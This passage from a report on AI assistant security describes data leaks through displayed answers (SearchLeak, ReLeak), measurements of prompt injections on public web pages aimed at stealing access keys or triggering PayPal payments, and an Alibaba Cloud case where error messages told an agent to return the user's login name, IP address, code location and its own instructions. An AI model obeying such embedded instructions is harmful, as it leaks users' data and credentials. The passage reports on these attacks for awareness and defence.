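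An AI product may have no published flaws because its vendor closes reports of data leaks through displayed answers as intended behaviour. Anyone choosing a product should therefore ask the vendor whether it treats such leaks as security bugs.

### Demonstrations and real attacks

Almost all the published leaks through displayed answers are demonstrations by researchers. Microsoft's advisory says that nobody exploited SearchLeak, and Infosecurity Magazine reports that Cato knew of no customers affected by ReLeak. OECD's *Critical SearchLeak Vulnerability in Microsoft 365 Copilot Exposes Sensitive Data*, an AI-generated entry in an incident database, contradicts the advisory by stating that attackers had exploited SearchLeak before the patch, but it cites no victim. The lack of known victims is only modest reassurance, because an image request that leaks data looks like ordinary web traffic,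 and many companies don't keep the records that would reveal one.

Prompt injections themselves do appear on public web pages. Google searched an archive that collects two to three billion web pages a month and found 32% more malicious injections in February 2026 than in November 2025, according to Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild* (2026). Some were meant to steal access keys. The security firm Forcepoint found others with complete instructions for a PayPal payment. Neither company found a sophisticated, coordinated campaign, although Forcepoint saw the same templates on several sites, which suggests shared tools.

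Those counts could be too high or too low. Google found that many matches were research papers and articles about prompt injection, which it had to separate from real attempts. The scan also left out social media, and a crawler of public pages can't reach emails, support tickets or shared documents, which carried the injections in most of the attacks on office assistants.

In December 2026 Alibaba Cloud turned out to be sending such instructions itself. The Hacker News' *Alibaba Cloud Got Caught Prompt-Injecting AI Agents* (2026) describes a developer whose agent was using the company's command-line tool when ordinary queries began to fail. Some error messages contained 7,153 bytes of English instructions for the agent to send back the computer's login name, its public IP address, the location of the project's code and the agent's own instructions. Alibaba said this was a measure against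 suspected automated abuse and that it would stop returning such prompts. The developer sent nothing, and there is no evidence that any other user's agent did. The text arrived over a connection with a valid certificate for Alibaba's own domain, so an agent that trusted text from known suppliers would have had no reason to doubt it.
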